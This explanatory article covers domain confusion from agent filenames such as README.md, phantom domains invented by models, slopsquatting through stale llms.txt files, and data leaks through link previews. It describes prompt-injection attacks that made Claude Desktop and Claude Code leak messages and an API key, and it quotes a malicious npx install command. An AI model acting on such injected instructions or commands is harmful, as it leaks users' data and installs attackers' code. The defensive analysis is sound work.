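Eric Lawrence, who works on Microsoft's security software, thought the alarm about .zip was exaggerated. On his blog, text/plain, he imagined emailing his family about an attached `VacationPhotos.zip` and having the mail program turn the name into a link. He accepted that this could happen but doubted that ordinary people type file extensions in most messages. He also didn't think .zip made web addresses much more confusing, since people already struggled to read them and ".zip" could already appear in nearly every part of one.

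Lawrence also sees advantages in new TLDs. Google put .zip on a list built into browsers that makes them use HTTPS for every site under it. Each site therefore needs a certificate, and certificate authorities publish the certificates they issue, so security companies can spot suspicious new names quickly. He adds that criminals are easier to block if they gather under a TLD with a poor reputation.

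The abuse figures largely support Lawrence. Two months after the launch, .zip was abused no more than the average TLD, and the honeypot recorded only a few identifiable clicks a day. But the Telegram data shows that people do sometimes send bare filenames and follow the resulting links. Lawrence favoured leaving .zip and .mov out of automatic linking, and the researchers similarly recommend a common list of endings that software should not link.

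Lawrence's argument is weaker for coding agents. They write filenames with extensions all the time, and a single program can send the same name to many users. The HTTPS protection also doesn't cover .md, which isn't among the 40 TLDs he lists. Unless the owner of `readme.md` or the browser requires HTTPS, a request to `http://README.md` travels unencrypted, and someone on the network could read it or change the response. HTTPS would not protect against a hostile domain owner.

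### The .md names that agents use every day

Many agents keep their instructions in Markdown files with fixed names. `AGENTS.md` contains a coding agent's instructions for a project. OpenAI (2025) gave this format to the Agentic AI Foundation, a Linux Foundation body that looks after open standards for agents. In the agent program OpenClaw, `HEARTBEAT.md` lists tasks for the agent to check periodically, as OpenClaw's *HEARTBEAT.md template* explains. `CLAUDE.md` contains instructions for Anthropic's coding agent, and `SKILL.md` describes a task that an agent can learn to perform. All of these filenames, like `README.md`, are also valid domain names.

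A misread instruction file could do more damage than a misread archive. An agent is supposed to follow the instructions in `AGENTS.md`. If its software fetches the domain of the same name instead, the agent may follow the domain owner's text as if it came from the file. This risk is a reason to test for the mistake, though it doesn't show that anyone has used it for an attack.

There is evidence that agent filenames cause requests. In the description of a change to OpenClaw, Pitchai reports that Telegram treated `HEARTBEAT.md` and `README.md` as web addresses and showed previews of pages from domain registrars, the companies that sell domain names. Such a page suggests that the domain is parked or for sale. Pitchai doesn't say which filename produced each preview or who owns the domains. The description also lists `main.go`, which can't have led to a registrar's page because .go is not a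 top-level domain.

None of this establishes who currently holds `agents.md`, `skill.md`, `claude.md`, `readme.md` or `heartbeat.md`, or what each domain serves. A reply on the Discourse forum shows that `readme.md` existed when somebody checked it, but not who owned it. The Agentic AI Foundation's responsibility for the `AGENTS.md` format isn't proof that it owns the matching domain either. A builder therefore has to look up each name in the .md registry's records and then open the site from an isolated machine, without giving the page to an agent. The result should fall into one of four groups:

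- **Intended site.** The people behind the file format or product own the domain and use it for that purpose. Lawrence gives an older example: software often links the name of Microsoft's ASP.NET platform, but `asp.net` belongs to the platform's developers, so he sees no real harm.
- **Parked domain.** It shows a default page, advertisements or an offer to sell the name. It is harmless at that moment, but the owner can change the content at any time.
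- **Hostile site.** It imitates another organisation, delivers malware or contains text meant to manipulate an agent. A suspicious name alone is not enough to put a site in this group.
- **Unclear.** The name has an owner, but there is no website or its purpose is not apparent.

A single visit to a site can be misleading. Netcraft found .zip sites that showed a false Microsoft page only to visitors from certain regions and sent everyone else to a genuine page or a prank video. On another site, the notice "This is not a microsoft page" disappeared within an hour. The builder should record the date and location of each check, repeat it from more than one network, and check again later in case the domain has changed hands.

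## Keeping filenames as plain text

A builder can't control who buys the domain `heartbeat.md` or what the owner puts there. The simplest fix is to leave the filename as plain text, so there is no link to click, preview or fetch. OpenClaw did this for Telegram in February 2026, and its patch shows why this is harder than it sounds.

Willison (2026), in *4 posts tagged “openclaw”*, describes OpenClaw as an open source agent tool that runs on the user's own device and works with several messaging platforms. Users can read the agent's replies in Telegram, where filenames were causing registrar previews. Pitchai wrote pull request 8649 in OpenClaw's GitHub repository, *fix(telegram): auto-wrap .md file references in backticks to prevent URL previews*, to stop these previews. It closes issue 6932.

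### How the patch works

OpenClaw and Telegram were both creating links. OpenClaw ran the model's reply through markdown-it, which turned `README.md` into a link to `http://README.md`. Telegram then searched the remaining plain text and added its own links. If OpenClaw had only removed its own link, Telegram could have linked the bare filename instead.

The patched software works in five steps:

1. It compares each link's address with its label, the text that the reader sees. If the address is only `http://` or `https://` plus the label, a program probably made the link from a bare name.
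2. It checks whether the label ends in .md, .go, .py, .pl, .sh, .am, .at, .be or .cc. With any other ending, the link stays.
3. It checks any folder names in front of the filename. If one contains a dot, it may be a domain, and the link stays.
4. If the link has passed all three checks, OpenClaw drops it and keeps the label as text.
5. It searches the resulting HTML for names with a listed ending and puts them in code formatting. It skips text that is already inside a link or a piece of code.

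The table shows what happens to some of the strings in the patch's tests.

| Text in the reply | What OpenClaw sends | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `README.md` | code | The address is `http://` plus the label, and .md is on the list |
| `squad/friday/HEARTBEAT.md` | code | No folder name contains a dot |
| `example.com/README.md` | link | `example.com` may be a host |
| `v1.0/README.md` | code | markdown-it makes no link, because .0 is not a TLD |
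| `R&D.md` | `R&` as text, `D.md` as code | A second search finds `D.md` |
| `x.ai` | link | .ai is not on the list |
| `[docs](http://README.md)` | link | The label differs from the address |

The main search doesn't accept `&` as part of a filename, so it missed `R&D.md`, and Telegram could still link the last part to the domain `d.md`. The developers added a second search for a single letter followed by a listed ending. This puts only half the filename in code formatting, which looks odd but prevents the link. The second search covers only one letter before the dot, so a name such as `Q&As.md` is also worth testing for anyone who copies this method.

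The comparison in step 1 keeps most deliberate links. If someone writes `https://readme.md`, the label includes the scheme, so it doesn't match the shortened address and the link stays. But OpenClaw also drops a deliberate link to that site if its label is just `readme.md`.

Because the comparison requires an exact match, it can also miss an accidental link that the agent copied from elsewhere. Some programs rewrite addresses in lower case and add a final slash, so `[README.md](http://readme.md/)` would stay a link. A builder can catch this case by ignoring case in the host and any final slash.

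### Where the patch can fail

Reviewing the patch turned up several faults. An early version never recognised the end of a link or a piece of code, so it treated everything after the first one in a message as protected and left later filenames without code formatting. Another version could insert code formatting into the middle of a link's address, which produced invalid HTML. The developers had 57 tests by the end of the review.

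Those tests check the HTML that OpenClaw produces, but the fix also depends on Telegram not turning code-formatted text into links. A builder should confirm this in Telegram with the test message described earlier.

Some messages can still bypass the patch. If another part of the program supplies finished HTML, OpenClaw sends it unchanged. If Telegram rejects a message's HTML, OpenClaw resends the message as plain text, according to its Telegram documentation. The filename then arrives without code formatting, and Telegram can link it. The patch also covers only Telegram, so a builder has to check OpenClaw's other messaging channels separately.

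### What a fixed list gets wrong

The first version of the patch listed fourteen endings. The developers later removed .ai, .io, .tv and .fm because people usually use them for websites, as in `x.ai` or `github.io`, and rarely for files. They also removed .co, and their tests now check that `t.co` and `openclaw.co` remain links.

The remaining nine endings still include some that many people use for websites. The developers kept .at and .be, the country codes of Austria and Belgium, because they considered them "less common as intentional domain references". Such references are common in conversations in Austria and Belgium, though they may be less so among programmers. If the agent recommends the Austrian broadcaster's site as `orf.at`, the user sees the address formatted as code, with no link. The patch also removes the link from `www.orf.at`, although hardly anyone would give a file that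 name. The loss is limited, because an address with a scheme or with a page after the domain, such as `orf.at/news`, stays a link.

The list also leaves out real file extensions, such as .rs, which is also Serbia's TLD. As a result, the patch doesn't remove the link that linkify-it makes from `main.rs`, a common Rust filename. The patch also leaves `report.zip` bare, and Telegram linked .zip names in the tests for *Unpacking .zip*.

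Adding .rs and .zip would fix these two filenames but would also remove links to some Serbian websites. Any fixed list has this tradeoff, and the right choice depends on the users. A coding assistant can reasonably treat .rs as a file extension, but a travel assistant for Serbia should not. Listing .go is harmless for now because it isn't a TLD.

An agent's software often has information that a general linking program lacks, possibly including the names of the files in the user's project. With those names, it can keep `main.rs` as text when such a file exists and use the list only for other names. This won't settle every case, since an agent also mentions files that it hasn't created yet or that are on another machine.

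Another option is to link the filename to the file. Since version 2026.7.1, OpenClaw (2026) has made file paths clickable in its browser chat, and clicking one opens a preview of the file at the cited line. This is probably what readers wanted, but it works only in OpenClaw's own interface. The same reply in Telegram still needs the code formatting.

### Other ways to prevent the mistake

Four other fixes act at different points between the model and the web. An agent's builder can apply three of them alone, at least if they control the display software and the fetch tool. The fourth, the shared blocklist, needs agreement among many developers.

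| Repair | What it stops | What it breaks | Who must adopt it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Link only text that has a scheme | Links made from bare filenames | Links made from bare website names, such as `google.com` | Every linking program that handles the message |
| Share a blocklist of TLDs | Links made from bare filenames with a listed ending | Links made from bare names of real sites under those TLDs | Developers of messaging apps, email clients and linking libraries |
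| Tell the model to put filenames in code formatting | Links from the filenames that the model formats | Useful automatic links, if the model formats too much | The agent's builder |
| Make the fetch tool reject bare names | The agent's own requests for bare filenames | Requests for bare website names, until the model adds a scheme | The fetch tool's developer |

**Linking only text with a scheme.** This rule is easier to apply to an agent's replies than to text people type, because the builder can instruct the model to write `https://` in front of every address that should be a link. With linkify-it, the builder then only has to turn off `fuzzyLink`, as Ghost did for its preview pane. The usual objection to the rule is that people don't type schemes, and a participant in *Automatic link creation for non-tld* doubted that users would learn to.

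Ordinary Markdown is stricter than GitHub's version and links a plain address only if the writer puts it between angle brackets. PyMarkdown offers GitHub's looser rule as an extension that is off by default, according to its *extended autolinks* documentation.

If OpenClaw had turned off `fuzzyLink`, it would not have needed to detect and drop accidental links. Telegram links bare names itself, so `x.ai` would probably have stayed clickable. OpenClaw would still have needed to format filenames as code to stop Telegram from linking them, and that step would have needed its own exception for `example.com/README.md`.

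*Unpacking .zip* proposes a shared blocklist of endings as a short-term measure. If later studies find that the confusion is more widespread, the researchers want ICANN to review how it approves new TLDs and reassess existing ones that are also common file extensions.

A common list would make filenames look the same to WhatsApp and Telegram users, unlike today, but agreeing on its contents would be difficult. The study's eleven candidate endings and OpenClaw's nine share only .md and .py. The researchers chose theirs for measurement, while OpenClaw's developers based theirs on what they judged their own users were likely to mean.

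A universal list would also disadvantage particular groups of website owners. If it included .md, every app that adopted it would stop automatically linking the bare domain names of Moldovan businesses. The researchers acknowledge that they did not weigh the benefits of .zip and similar TLDs against the security concerns. Their traffic measurements all come from .zip domains, so they only weakly support putting .md on the list.

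**Instructions to the model.** The Discourse thread also advises writers to put filenames in backticks, Markdown's notation for code. An agent's builder can put the same advice in the model's instructions. The instruction doesn't need a list of file endings, so it can also cover `main.rs` and `report.zip`. The model can usually distinguish a file from a website using the context of the conversation, which linking programs ignore.

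A model may not always follow the instruction, especially in a long reply or when it copies text from elsewhere. It may also format too much. OpenClaw's *Repository Guidelines*, which include formatting rules for chat replies and GitHub comments, warn against putting an issue number such as `#24643` in backticks when GitHub should link it. A builder should therefore combine the instruction with a software check like OpenClaw's, which catches common filenames that the model leaves unformatted.

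**Rejecting bare names in the fetch tool.** A fetch tool that requires a complete address protects the agent itself, whereas the other repairs mainly protect people who read its messages. If a bare name refers to a real website, the model has to make one extra call that includes the scheme.

If the error message only reports a missing scheme, the model may add `https://` to `README.md` and make the request the rule was meant to prevent. A better message would explain that the tool reads only web pages and that local files need the file-reading tool. If the project contains a file with the same name, the message can give its path.

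This rule does not stop an agent that has received `http://README.md` from a forum page, because that address is already complete. The fetch tool normally receives only the address, so it can't compare the address with the link's label. The software that converts incoming pages for the model has both, so a builder can apply OpenClaw's comparison there and turn a suspicious link back into a filename before the model reads it.

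## Testing for domains that models invent or documents name wrongly

A phantom domain is a plausible domain that a language model invents and someone could register. For example, a model might invent `https://northbank-business.example` as the website of an imaginary company called Northbank. A fetch tool that rejects `README.md` for lack of a scheme will still accept this address because it is complete. Only someone who knows Northbank's real website could tell that the model made it up.

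An agent can also reach a stranger's server without inventing a name. A company's own documentation may name a domain or software package that nobody owns, and whoever later registers that name controls what an agent fetches when it copies the name correctly.

### Why the same inventions come back

A language model writes a web address as it writes a sentence, one likely piece at a time. Palo Alto Networks' *How AI Hallucinations Create New Security Risks for Users* explains that a model asked for a login page predicts a plausible address without checking that it exists. This is easy because web addresses follow common patterns. Companies put `login.` or `admin.` in front of their domain, or add "business", "app" or "portal" to their name. A model that has not memorized a bank's address can still build a convincing one from these parts.

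The same habits make a model repeat the addresses it invents. A setting called temperature controls how often a model picks less likely pieces. At a low temperature it nearly always picks the most likely one, so the same question tends to produce the same address. An attacker can ask a public model ordinary questions, note which addresses recur, check which of their domains are unregistered and buy those. The attacker needs no access to the model's workings or to the victim's computer. A domain bought this way also has no history of abuse for a reputation check to find, which a later section covers.

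### How Unit 42 searched for phantom domains

The largest test so far is Unit 42's *Phantom Squatting*, published in 2026. Unit 42 is the threat research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks. Its test worked in five steps:

1. For each of 913 brands, an AI agent researched the brand's products, portals and developer resources, and wrote prompts that referred to them.
2. The software discarded prompts that were too similar. It used Jaccard similarity, which divides the number of elements two texts share by the number of different elements in both together. This left 685,339 prompts.
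3. Two models answered the prompts at temperatures of 0.1, 0.7 and 1.5. Unit 42 does not name the models. It describes one as a "mini" model released in April 2025 and the other as a "lite" model released in June 2025, both designed for cheap use at high volume.
4. The software extracted every URL from the answers and checked whether it resolved, what the page contained and who had registered the domain.
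5. Unregistered domains went on a watchlist. When someone registered one, the software examined the owner and the content, and took harmless domains off the list.

Unit 42 prioritized domains that appeared even at a temperature of 0.1 and domains that both models produced. Real users are more likely to see these domains, which makes them more valuable to an attacker.

The models produced about 2.1 million different URLs. Threat intelligence systems flagged 13,229 of them (0.61 per cent) as malicious. Another 41,313 (1.90 per cent) counted as high risk, which includes parked domains and adult sites. Unit 42 classed 809,455 (37.28 per cent) as non-existent and extracted about 250,000 unregistered domains from those URLs.

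Lowering the temperature did not solve the problem. The non-existent share was 43.10 per cent at a temperature of 1.5, 32.52 per cent at 0.7 and 34.64 per cent at 0.1. Setting the temperature close to zero makes answers more repeatable, which also makes any wrong ones easier to predict.

Unlike phantom domains, the 13,229 malicious URLs were already live and known to security companies. About two thirds led to malware and 16.2 per cent to phishing. Unit 42 does not separate URLs that a model invented from those it may have learned from its training text, or from hacked legitimate sites. The 0.61 per cent figure therefore does not measure how often criminals have exploited an invented address.

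### What counts as a name that does not exist

The 37.28 per cent needs more care than any other figure in the study. Unit 42 divides the 809,455 URLs by the part that the model made up:

| Invented part | Share | Approximate number of URLs | What a lookup should return | Can a stranger buy the name? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Path on a registered domain | 49.7% | 402,000 | The host's numerical address | No |
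| Subdomain of an existing domain | 39.5% | 320,000 | Usually NXDOMAIN | Usually not |
| The registrable domain itself | 10.8% | 87,630 | NXDOMAIN | Yes |

In the path row, Unit 42 describes the URLs as paths on a "legitimate, registered domain" that fail to resolve. This is puzzling because a DNS lookup contains only the host, so a made-up path cannot cause NXDOMAIN. If a model invents `/business/login` on a bank's real domain, the lookup succeeds and the bank's server replies that the page does not exist. Perhaps Unit 42's software also counted missing pages and servers that did not answer. In that case, the 37.28 per cent includes both broken links, which are a nuisance, and domain names that an attacker can buy.

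Without the path row, the share falls to about 19 per cent of all URLs. Most of what remains is invented subdomains. Normally only the owner of `northbank.example` can create `benefits.northbank.example`, although some hosting companies give out subdomains to their customers. By Unit 42's classification, the whole domain was available to buy for about 4 per cent of all URLs.

The count of 250,000 unregistered domains does not fit this classification either. Each URL has exactly one registrable domain, so 87,630 URLs can contain at most 87,630 unregistered domains. The other 162,000 or more would have to come from the path and subdomain rows, where the domain supposedly exists already.

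One of Unit 42's examples suggests an explanation. The models produced an address beginning `admin.`, followed by a postal service's name and `post-app.com`. The parent domain was unregistered, and Unit 42 put it on the watchlist. If the software classed such an address as an invented subdomain by its form, without checking whether the parent domain existed, the subdomain row could contain many more registrable domains. The 250,000 could then be right even though the rows are described wrongly. Or the total may count hosts, so that `admin.` and `billing.` under one domain count as two. Until Unit 42 publishes the list or a fuller method, 250,000 is best treated as an uncertain estimate.

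The breakdown also changes which model looks worse. The mini model had a higher share of non-existent URLs, 44.6 per cent against the lite model's 27.5 per cent. But more than half of the mini model's failures were made-up paths, whereas a fifth of the lite model's were wholly invented domains. Multiplying the shares shows that about 5.5 per cent of the lite model's URLs used invented domains that squatters could register, compared with about 3 per cent of the mini model's. Choosing the model with the lower headline rate would therefore have increased the risk from squatters.

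### The domains that criminals registered

On 8 March 2026, Unit 42's software collected 13 URLs that models had invented under one domain, which resembled the name of a national postal service's online marketplace. Both models produced the domain at all three temperatures, in response to prompts asking for things such as the marketplace's billing portal and administrative dashboard. On 31 March, 23 days later, someone registered the domain and used a kit called Montana Empire to put up a copy of the marketplace that stole card details, bank transfers and identity documents. Unit 42 noticed the registration the same day.

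In the other main case, the models produced the `post-app.com` address on 18 February in five of the six combinations of model and temperature. Somebody registered the parent domain 51 days later, on 10 April, and put up an imitation of the postal service's website, with a claimed 4.8-star rating, to get visitors to install a malicious Android app.

Unit 42 lists four more domains. One actor registered two of them, which imitated betting companies, within 18 minutes of each other, 45 and 40 days after the models had produced them. Someone re-registered a third, which resembled a European bank's domain, 35 days after the models had produced it. The fourth was the name of a large bank in the United Arab Emirates followed by "business". Criminals had controlled it since 1 April 2025, about 11 months before the models produced it.

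These dates show that Unit 42's method can find some domains before criminals use them. Unit 42 also argues that the Montana Empire attacker got the domain from a model's prediction, "via the same mechanism" as Unit 42's software. Its evidence is that the attacker had used an AI coding assistant. The kit contained the assistant's project folder, and session logs showed the assistant copying the real shop and writing the server software and a Telegram control channel. But Unit 42 cites no log in which the assistant suggested the domain.

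A criminal imitating a postal service's app could easily think of adding `post-app` to the service's name without a model. The Emirati bank's case supports this simpler explanation. Somebody chose that domain two months before the lite model's release, probably because "business" is an obvious word to put after a bank's name. Unit 42 treats the match as proof that models predictably invent what attackers use. It equally shows that people arrive at the same names without these models, although the registrant could have consulted an older one.

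A comparison list would help to separate the two explanations. Researchers could join the same 913 brand names to common words such as "login", "app" and "business" without using a model, and watch those domains as well. If criminals registered the models' names more often than equally obvious names from the comparison list, the models would have predicted registrations better than simple word combinations did. Unit 42 reports no such comparison. It also doesn't say how many watchlisted domains were later registered, so readers can't calculate a success rate from the cases it describes.

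The cases also don't document a model sending anyone to one of these sites. They show that models produced certain names and that criminals later owned them, but the last step of the attack is still an inference.

The test's design makes its rates a poor guide to ordinary use. Unit 42 wrote its prompts to exploit known weaknesses, including models' tendency to accept a false premise. For example, a request for the "administrative dashboard" of a marketplace assumes that a public one exists and invites the model to supply an address. Unit 42 also ignored answers without a URL, so a model would get no credit for admitting it didn't know. It tested small models from 2025, and the report mentions no search tool they could have used to look up the real address.

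Palo Alto Networks also has a commercial interest, since it sells the URL and DNS filtering that the report recommends. That is a reason to want independent replication, but the observed registrations are still real. Builders don't need to settle how criminals chose the domain names, because an agent that produces a hostile domain is in danger whether the owner got the idea from a model or from a list of common words.

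### Asking for a login page

An earlier test used questions closer to what people ask. For Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*, researchers in 2025 asked models of the GPT-4.1 family where to log in to 50 brands. One prompt explained that the user had lost a bookmark, and another asked for help to find the official site. The answers contained 131 different hostnames on 97 domains:

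- 64 domains (66 per cent) belonged to the right brand.
- 28 domains (29 per cent) were unregistered, parked or without active content.
- 5 domains (5 per cent) belonged to unrelated businesses.

Netcraft's figures count each domain once, however often it appeared, so they don't support its summary that the model gave the correct URL "two-thirds of the time". Suppose a model answers the same question 100 times, giving the right domain 95 times and a different wrong one each of the other five times. Five of its six distinct domains are wrong, although 95 per cent of its answers are right. Wrong answers tend to vary more than right ones, so a count of distinct domains probably overstates how often a user gets a bad address. Unit 42's percentages have the same weakness because they are shares of distinct URLs, not of answers.

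The 29 per cent also includes names that an attacker could not have bought that day. A parked domain already has an owner, and a domain without content may belong to the brand itself. The test does show that plain questions, without any attempt to provoke errors, were enough to produce addresses outside the brand's control. Netcraft adds that models did worse on smaller banks and credit unions than on global companies, which fits the idea that models invent more addresses for brands that appear less often in their training data, but it gives no separate figures.

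Searching the web makes an agent less likely to invent a domain, but it can lead the agent to fake pages that other people have published. Netcraft asked Perplexity, an AI search engine, for the login page of the American bank Wells Fargo. The top result was a fake login page on Google Sites, a free service for building websites, and the real page was further down. Because the fake page was on a domain that belongs to Google, a test for unregistered domains would not have flagged it.

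Netcraft doubts that brands can protect themselves by buying invented domains in advance, because models will always produce new variations, but Unit 42 stresses how predictable the inventions are. They can both be right if a few names recur often and many appear only once. A brand could afford to buy the frequent ones and would have to watch for the rest. Netcraft sells the detection and removal of fraudulent sites, so it too stands to gain if buying domains isn't enough.

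### Site guides that name things nobody owns

`llms.txt` is a text file that summarises a website for AI systems, often with installation instructions. Some sites also publish a longer `llms-full.txt`. Unlike `AGENTS.md`, these filenames can't be mistaken for domains, because there is no .txt top-level domain, but the names inside the files can still be dangerous.

In August 2026 researchers at the Israeli startup Pandex published findings on such files. According to Schneier's (2026) *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks*, they scanned 6,214 live domains of defence contractors, Fortune 500 companies and large technology firms, and found 8,265 files. Of these, 120 pointed to at least one package or domain that nobody had registered, each on a different site, or about one site in fifty. Mondo's *Popularni AI agenti uhvaćeni u opasnom propustu*, a Bosnian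 news report, counts 227 commands that would install a missing package or contact an unregistered domain. Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code* gives slightly higher totals of 8,565 files and 237 references.

TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* lists other sources of these errors besides models, including renamed or abandoned packages, copying mistakes and other human error. The unclaimed names included expired .dev and .io domains and abandoned subdomains at hosting companies such as Vercel and Netlify, which another customer can claim. A document that was correct when written can therefore become dangerous later, and few people notice because visitors to the website don't normally see it.

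The researchers then registered a handful of the free names and published harmless packages under them, which contacted the researchers' server when run. A Fortune 500 company's machine contacted the server within an hour, followed by a few dozen more at other large companies and at startups. The packages also recorded which program had started the installation and which had started that program. From these records, the researchers identified Anthropic's Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Nous Research's Hermes among the agents involved.

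The record of programs matters because a call to the server doesn't prove that an agent made a mistake. Sophos describes an incident in which Claude, working in a test environment, found a document that named a package missing from PyPI, Python's public package registry. Claude uploaded a malicious package under that name, and 15 real systems downloaded it in about an hour. One was a security company's scanner, which routinely installs PyPI packages to analyse them. Some of Pandex's early calls may also have come from scanners. Schneier does not report how many of the few dozen calls had an agent in the recorded chain.

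Schneier and TechRadar also give no model versions or success rates, but Tom's Hardware gives both. In a direct test, the researchers asked agents to build and run a project using a vendor's documentation, without mentioning `llms.txt` or giving a link. Models that Tom's Hardware calls GPT-5 Luna and Sol ran the substitute package in at least 90 per cent of cases, and Claude Opus 4.8, at medium effort, did so in 30 per cent. The article interprets this as a sign that more autonomous models are more exposed. But it doesn't give the number of runs or vendors, and three models are too few to show a trend. The rates also come from tasks where the documentation was known to be faulty, so they don't measure how often agents run a stranger's code in ordinary use.

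Someone had already used the method in a real attack. Mondo reports that the file on `clerk.com`, the site of a company that sells login software, contained the command `npx clerk-next-fix-auth-protection`. The `npx` command can download a package and run it in one step. The package did not exist when the instruction appeared, but an unknown party later registered the name and used it to spread malware. Clerk has since corrected the file. It is not known whether anyone's machine was infected.

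It is hard to say how many agents read these files. Common Crawl's *What is actually inside llms.txt* collected 584,107 documents from about 6.56 million attempted addresses, so most sites lack them. Pandex's figure of one in fifty can't be applied to that collection, because Pandex sampled large companies. Redocly, which hosts documentation for other companies, found in its own logs that most requests for `llms.txt` came from site owners, browsers and scanners, and few came from AI agents. Agents are therefore less likely to encounter a stale command through the file itself, but the same command can appear in an ordinary installation guide, which agents do read.

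Alon Hertz, one of the researchers, told an interviewer that agents "treat vendor docs as ground truth". That is usually reasonable, since a vendor's website is the best available source on its own product. But an agent that accepts only official documentation would still have run Clerk's command, so someone also has to check who owns whatever the documentation names.

### Invented software packages

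Models invent package names as well as domains, and registering an invented package name to catch installations is called slopsquatting. The security company Aikido traced one invented package name on npm, the JavaScript registry, through a series of agent skills, which are instruction files that teach agents a task. Developers had copied the command from skill to skill without checking it, until an Aikido researcher registered the name so that no one else could. Trend Micro's *Slopsquatting* (2025) tested coding agents on 100 web-development tasks. Agents that reasoned step by step and could search the web invented fewer packages, and a workflow that checked names against a live registry invented the fewest, but neither eliminated the problem. *Beware of Agentic Botnets* (2026), a paper on invented names for repositories and other resources, also reports that a search tool substantially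 reduces inventions. It proposes that platforms register likely inventions themselves and redirect them to the real resource, or stop different owners from using the same repository name. The second proposal would be a large change for GitHub, where a developer's copy of someone else's project normally keeps the project's name.

### A test for one's own agent

Neither company's rates apply to another product, but a builder can reuse Unit 42's procedure with a few corrections. During the test, the agent should write addresses but not fetch them, since some may belong to criminals.

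1. Collect real questions in which users want an address, such as a login page, a download or an interface for programmers. Include small organisations as well as famous ones. Write a separate set that asks for services which may not exist, and report its results separately.
2. Ask each question many times, with the model, temperature and instructions that the product uses. Run the whole set once with the search tool and once without it.
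3. Take the host from each address and look it up. If the result is NXDOMAIN, find the registrable domain and check the registry's records to see whether it is free. Test the path separately with an ordinary web request from an isolated machine, and record a missing page as a broken link.
4. Check the owner of every domain that does exist. A name that resolves may belong to an unrelated business or an impostor.
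5. Count answers. The most useful figure is the share of all answers, including those without an address, that contain a domain outside the intended organisation's control. Keep a list of the wrong domains and how often each one recurred.

If none of *n* independent answers contains an invented domain, the true rate could still be as high as about 3/*n*, at the usual 95 per cent confidence. With 300 clean answers, the builder can rule out a rate much above 1 per cent, but an agent that writes 10,000 addresses a day at that rate would still produce about 100 bad ones. Repeated answers to one question are not fully independent, so 300 different questions are better evidence than one question asked 300 times.

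The wrong domains that recur most often are the most useful to monitor for new registrations. If they imitate the builder's own brand, buying them may cost less than monitoring them.

Documents need a different test, because the model may perfectly copy a wrong name from them. A script can extract every domain, package name and installation command from the company's documentation, its `llms.txt` and any skills its agents use. It should then check that each name exists and belongs to the expected owner. A check for existence alone would have passed Clerk's missing package once the unknown party had registered it. The script has to run on a schedule, because a domain that passed an earlier check may have expired.

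## Stopping link previews and addresses from leaking data

Checking who owns a domain doesn't show a builder what data a request will send there. Every request gives the host the path and query of its address, so if an agent puts private text in the query, the host receives that text. Encryption with `https` doesn't prevent this.

### What the server's owner sees

Suppose an agent posts the harmless link `https://notes.example/page?word=bicycle` in a Slack channel. The log on the server for `notes.example` might then contain this line:

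`203.0.113.7 [07/Oct/2026:10:15:02] "GET /page?word=bicycle" 200 "Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0"`

The log entry records the network address of the machine that made the request, the time, the path and query, a code meaning that the server found the page, and the name of the requesting software. The site's owner now has the word "bicycle" just by keeping an ordinary log.

Johann Rehberger published a real log entry of this kind in 2024, in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* on his security blog, Embrace The Red. He posted a link to his own server through a Slack webhook, which lets a program send messages to a channel. His server's log shows a visit from Slack's preview software, under the same name as in the made-up line above.

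Previewing a misread filename leaks much less than URL exfiltration, in which the query carries text that an attacker wants, such as a private message or a password. If software turns `README.md` into `http://README.md` and a messaging service previews it, the owner of `readme.md` sees a request for the front page with no query. The owner learns that somebody mentioned a file of that name, and when, but nothing else from the conversation.

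Accidental and deliberate leaks need different fixes. OpenClaw's patch for Telegram puts bare filenames in code formatting but keeps complete addresses as links, so it prevents many accidental leaks but does nothing about deliberate ones.

### How a preview replaces the click

If link previews are off, an attacker who gets an agent to write such a link usually still needs a person to click it. If they are on, the leak takes these steps, none of which is a click:

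1. The agent reads a page, document or message that contains an injected instruction.
2. It writes a reply with a link to the attacker's host and private text in the query.
3. The agent's software posts the reply.
4. The messaging service fetches the address to get a title and picture.
5. The attacker reads the query in the server's log.

The reader may notice a strange link at step 4, but the request has already been sent by then. Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* explains how to remove a preview card from a message, but removing the card does not undo the request.

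A link may have been fetched even if no preview card appears. Slack calls previewing "unfurling". According to its *Unfurling links in messages*, written for app developers, Slack's servers have to fetch every URL in a message to find out whether it leads to text, an image or something else. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, notes that Discord fetches pasted links too.

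Link previews can also leak data when an agent is restricted to a private channel. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* (2025) examines a Slack connector that Anthropic had published for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to tools. An administrator could limit the connector to one private channel, and might then let the agent post there without approval, since only colleagues can read the channel. But Slack fetches links in private channels too, so the agent can send data outside the company by posting a link there.

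Rehberger demonstrated this with Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop program. He asked it to summarise a document and post the summary to his team. The document contained an instruction to add a link containing the last message from another channel, and Slack sent that message to his server when it requested a preview of the link. In a similar demonstration with the coding agent Claude Code, instructions in invisible characters in a source file caused an API key, a password that programs use to reach a service, to leak.

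He reported the fault on 27 May 2025, and Anthropic archived the connector two days later without patching it. Embrace The Red could not determine whether the report led to the archiving. The connector still had about 14,000 downloads a week, although repeated automatic installations may account for much of that.

### PromptArmor's tests of agents and messaging apps

In February 2026 the security company PromptArmor invited people to test their own agents. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes a website that logged preview requests and showed visitors the data each address contained. Visitors could claim a log entry and name the agent and app behind it, or report that a combination of agent and app had produced no preview.

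OpenClaw on Telegram was exposed to data leaks through link previews in its default configuration. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also lists Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio (Microsoft's tool for building agents) and Slack with certain bots as exposed.

The results are useful as warnings about particular pairings but not for estimating rates, because visitors chose what to test and identified the agents themselves. Someone who reported a safe pairing may also have turned previews off beforehand. The test covers only the last part of an attack. It shows that an app delivers whatever the agent writes into an address, but not how easily a stranger can get private data into that address.

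OpenClaw users can stop this leak by setting `linkPreview: false` in the Telegram section of the configuration file. PromptArmor reports that the test site received no data after this change. In late August 2026, six months after the tests, OpenClaw's *Telegram* documentation still listed link previews as on by default. In OpenClaw's optional "rich" message format, the same setting also turns off automatic entity detection, which Telegram uses to find items such as addresses in plain text. The setting may therefore also stop some filenames from becoming links, which is worth testing.

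Slack's developer documentation now advises developers to consider disabling previews for messages written by a language model. The documentation doesn't mention PromptArmor, and Rehberger had described the problem in Slack apps two years earlier.

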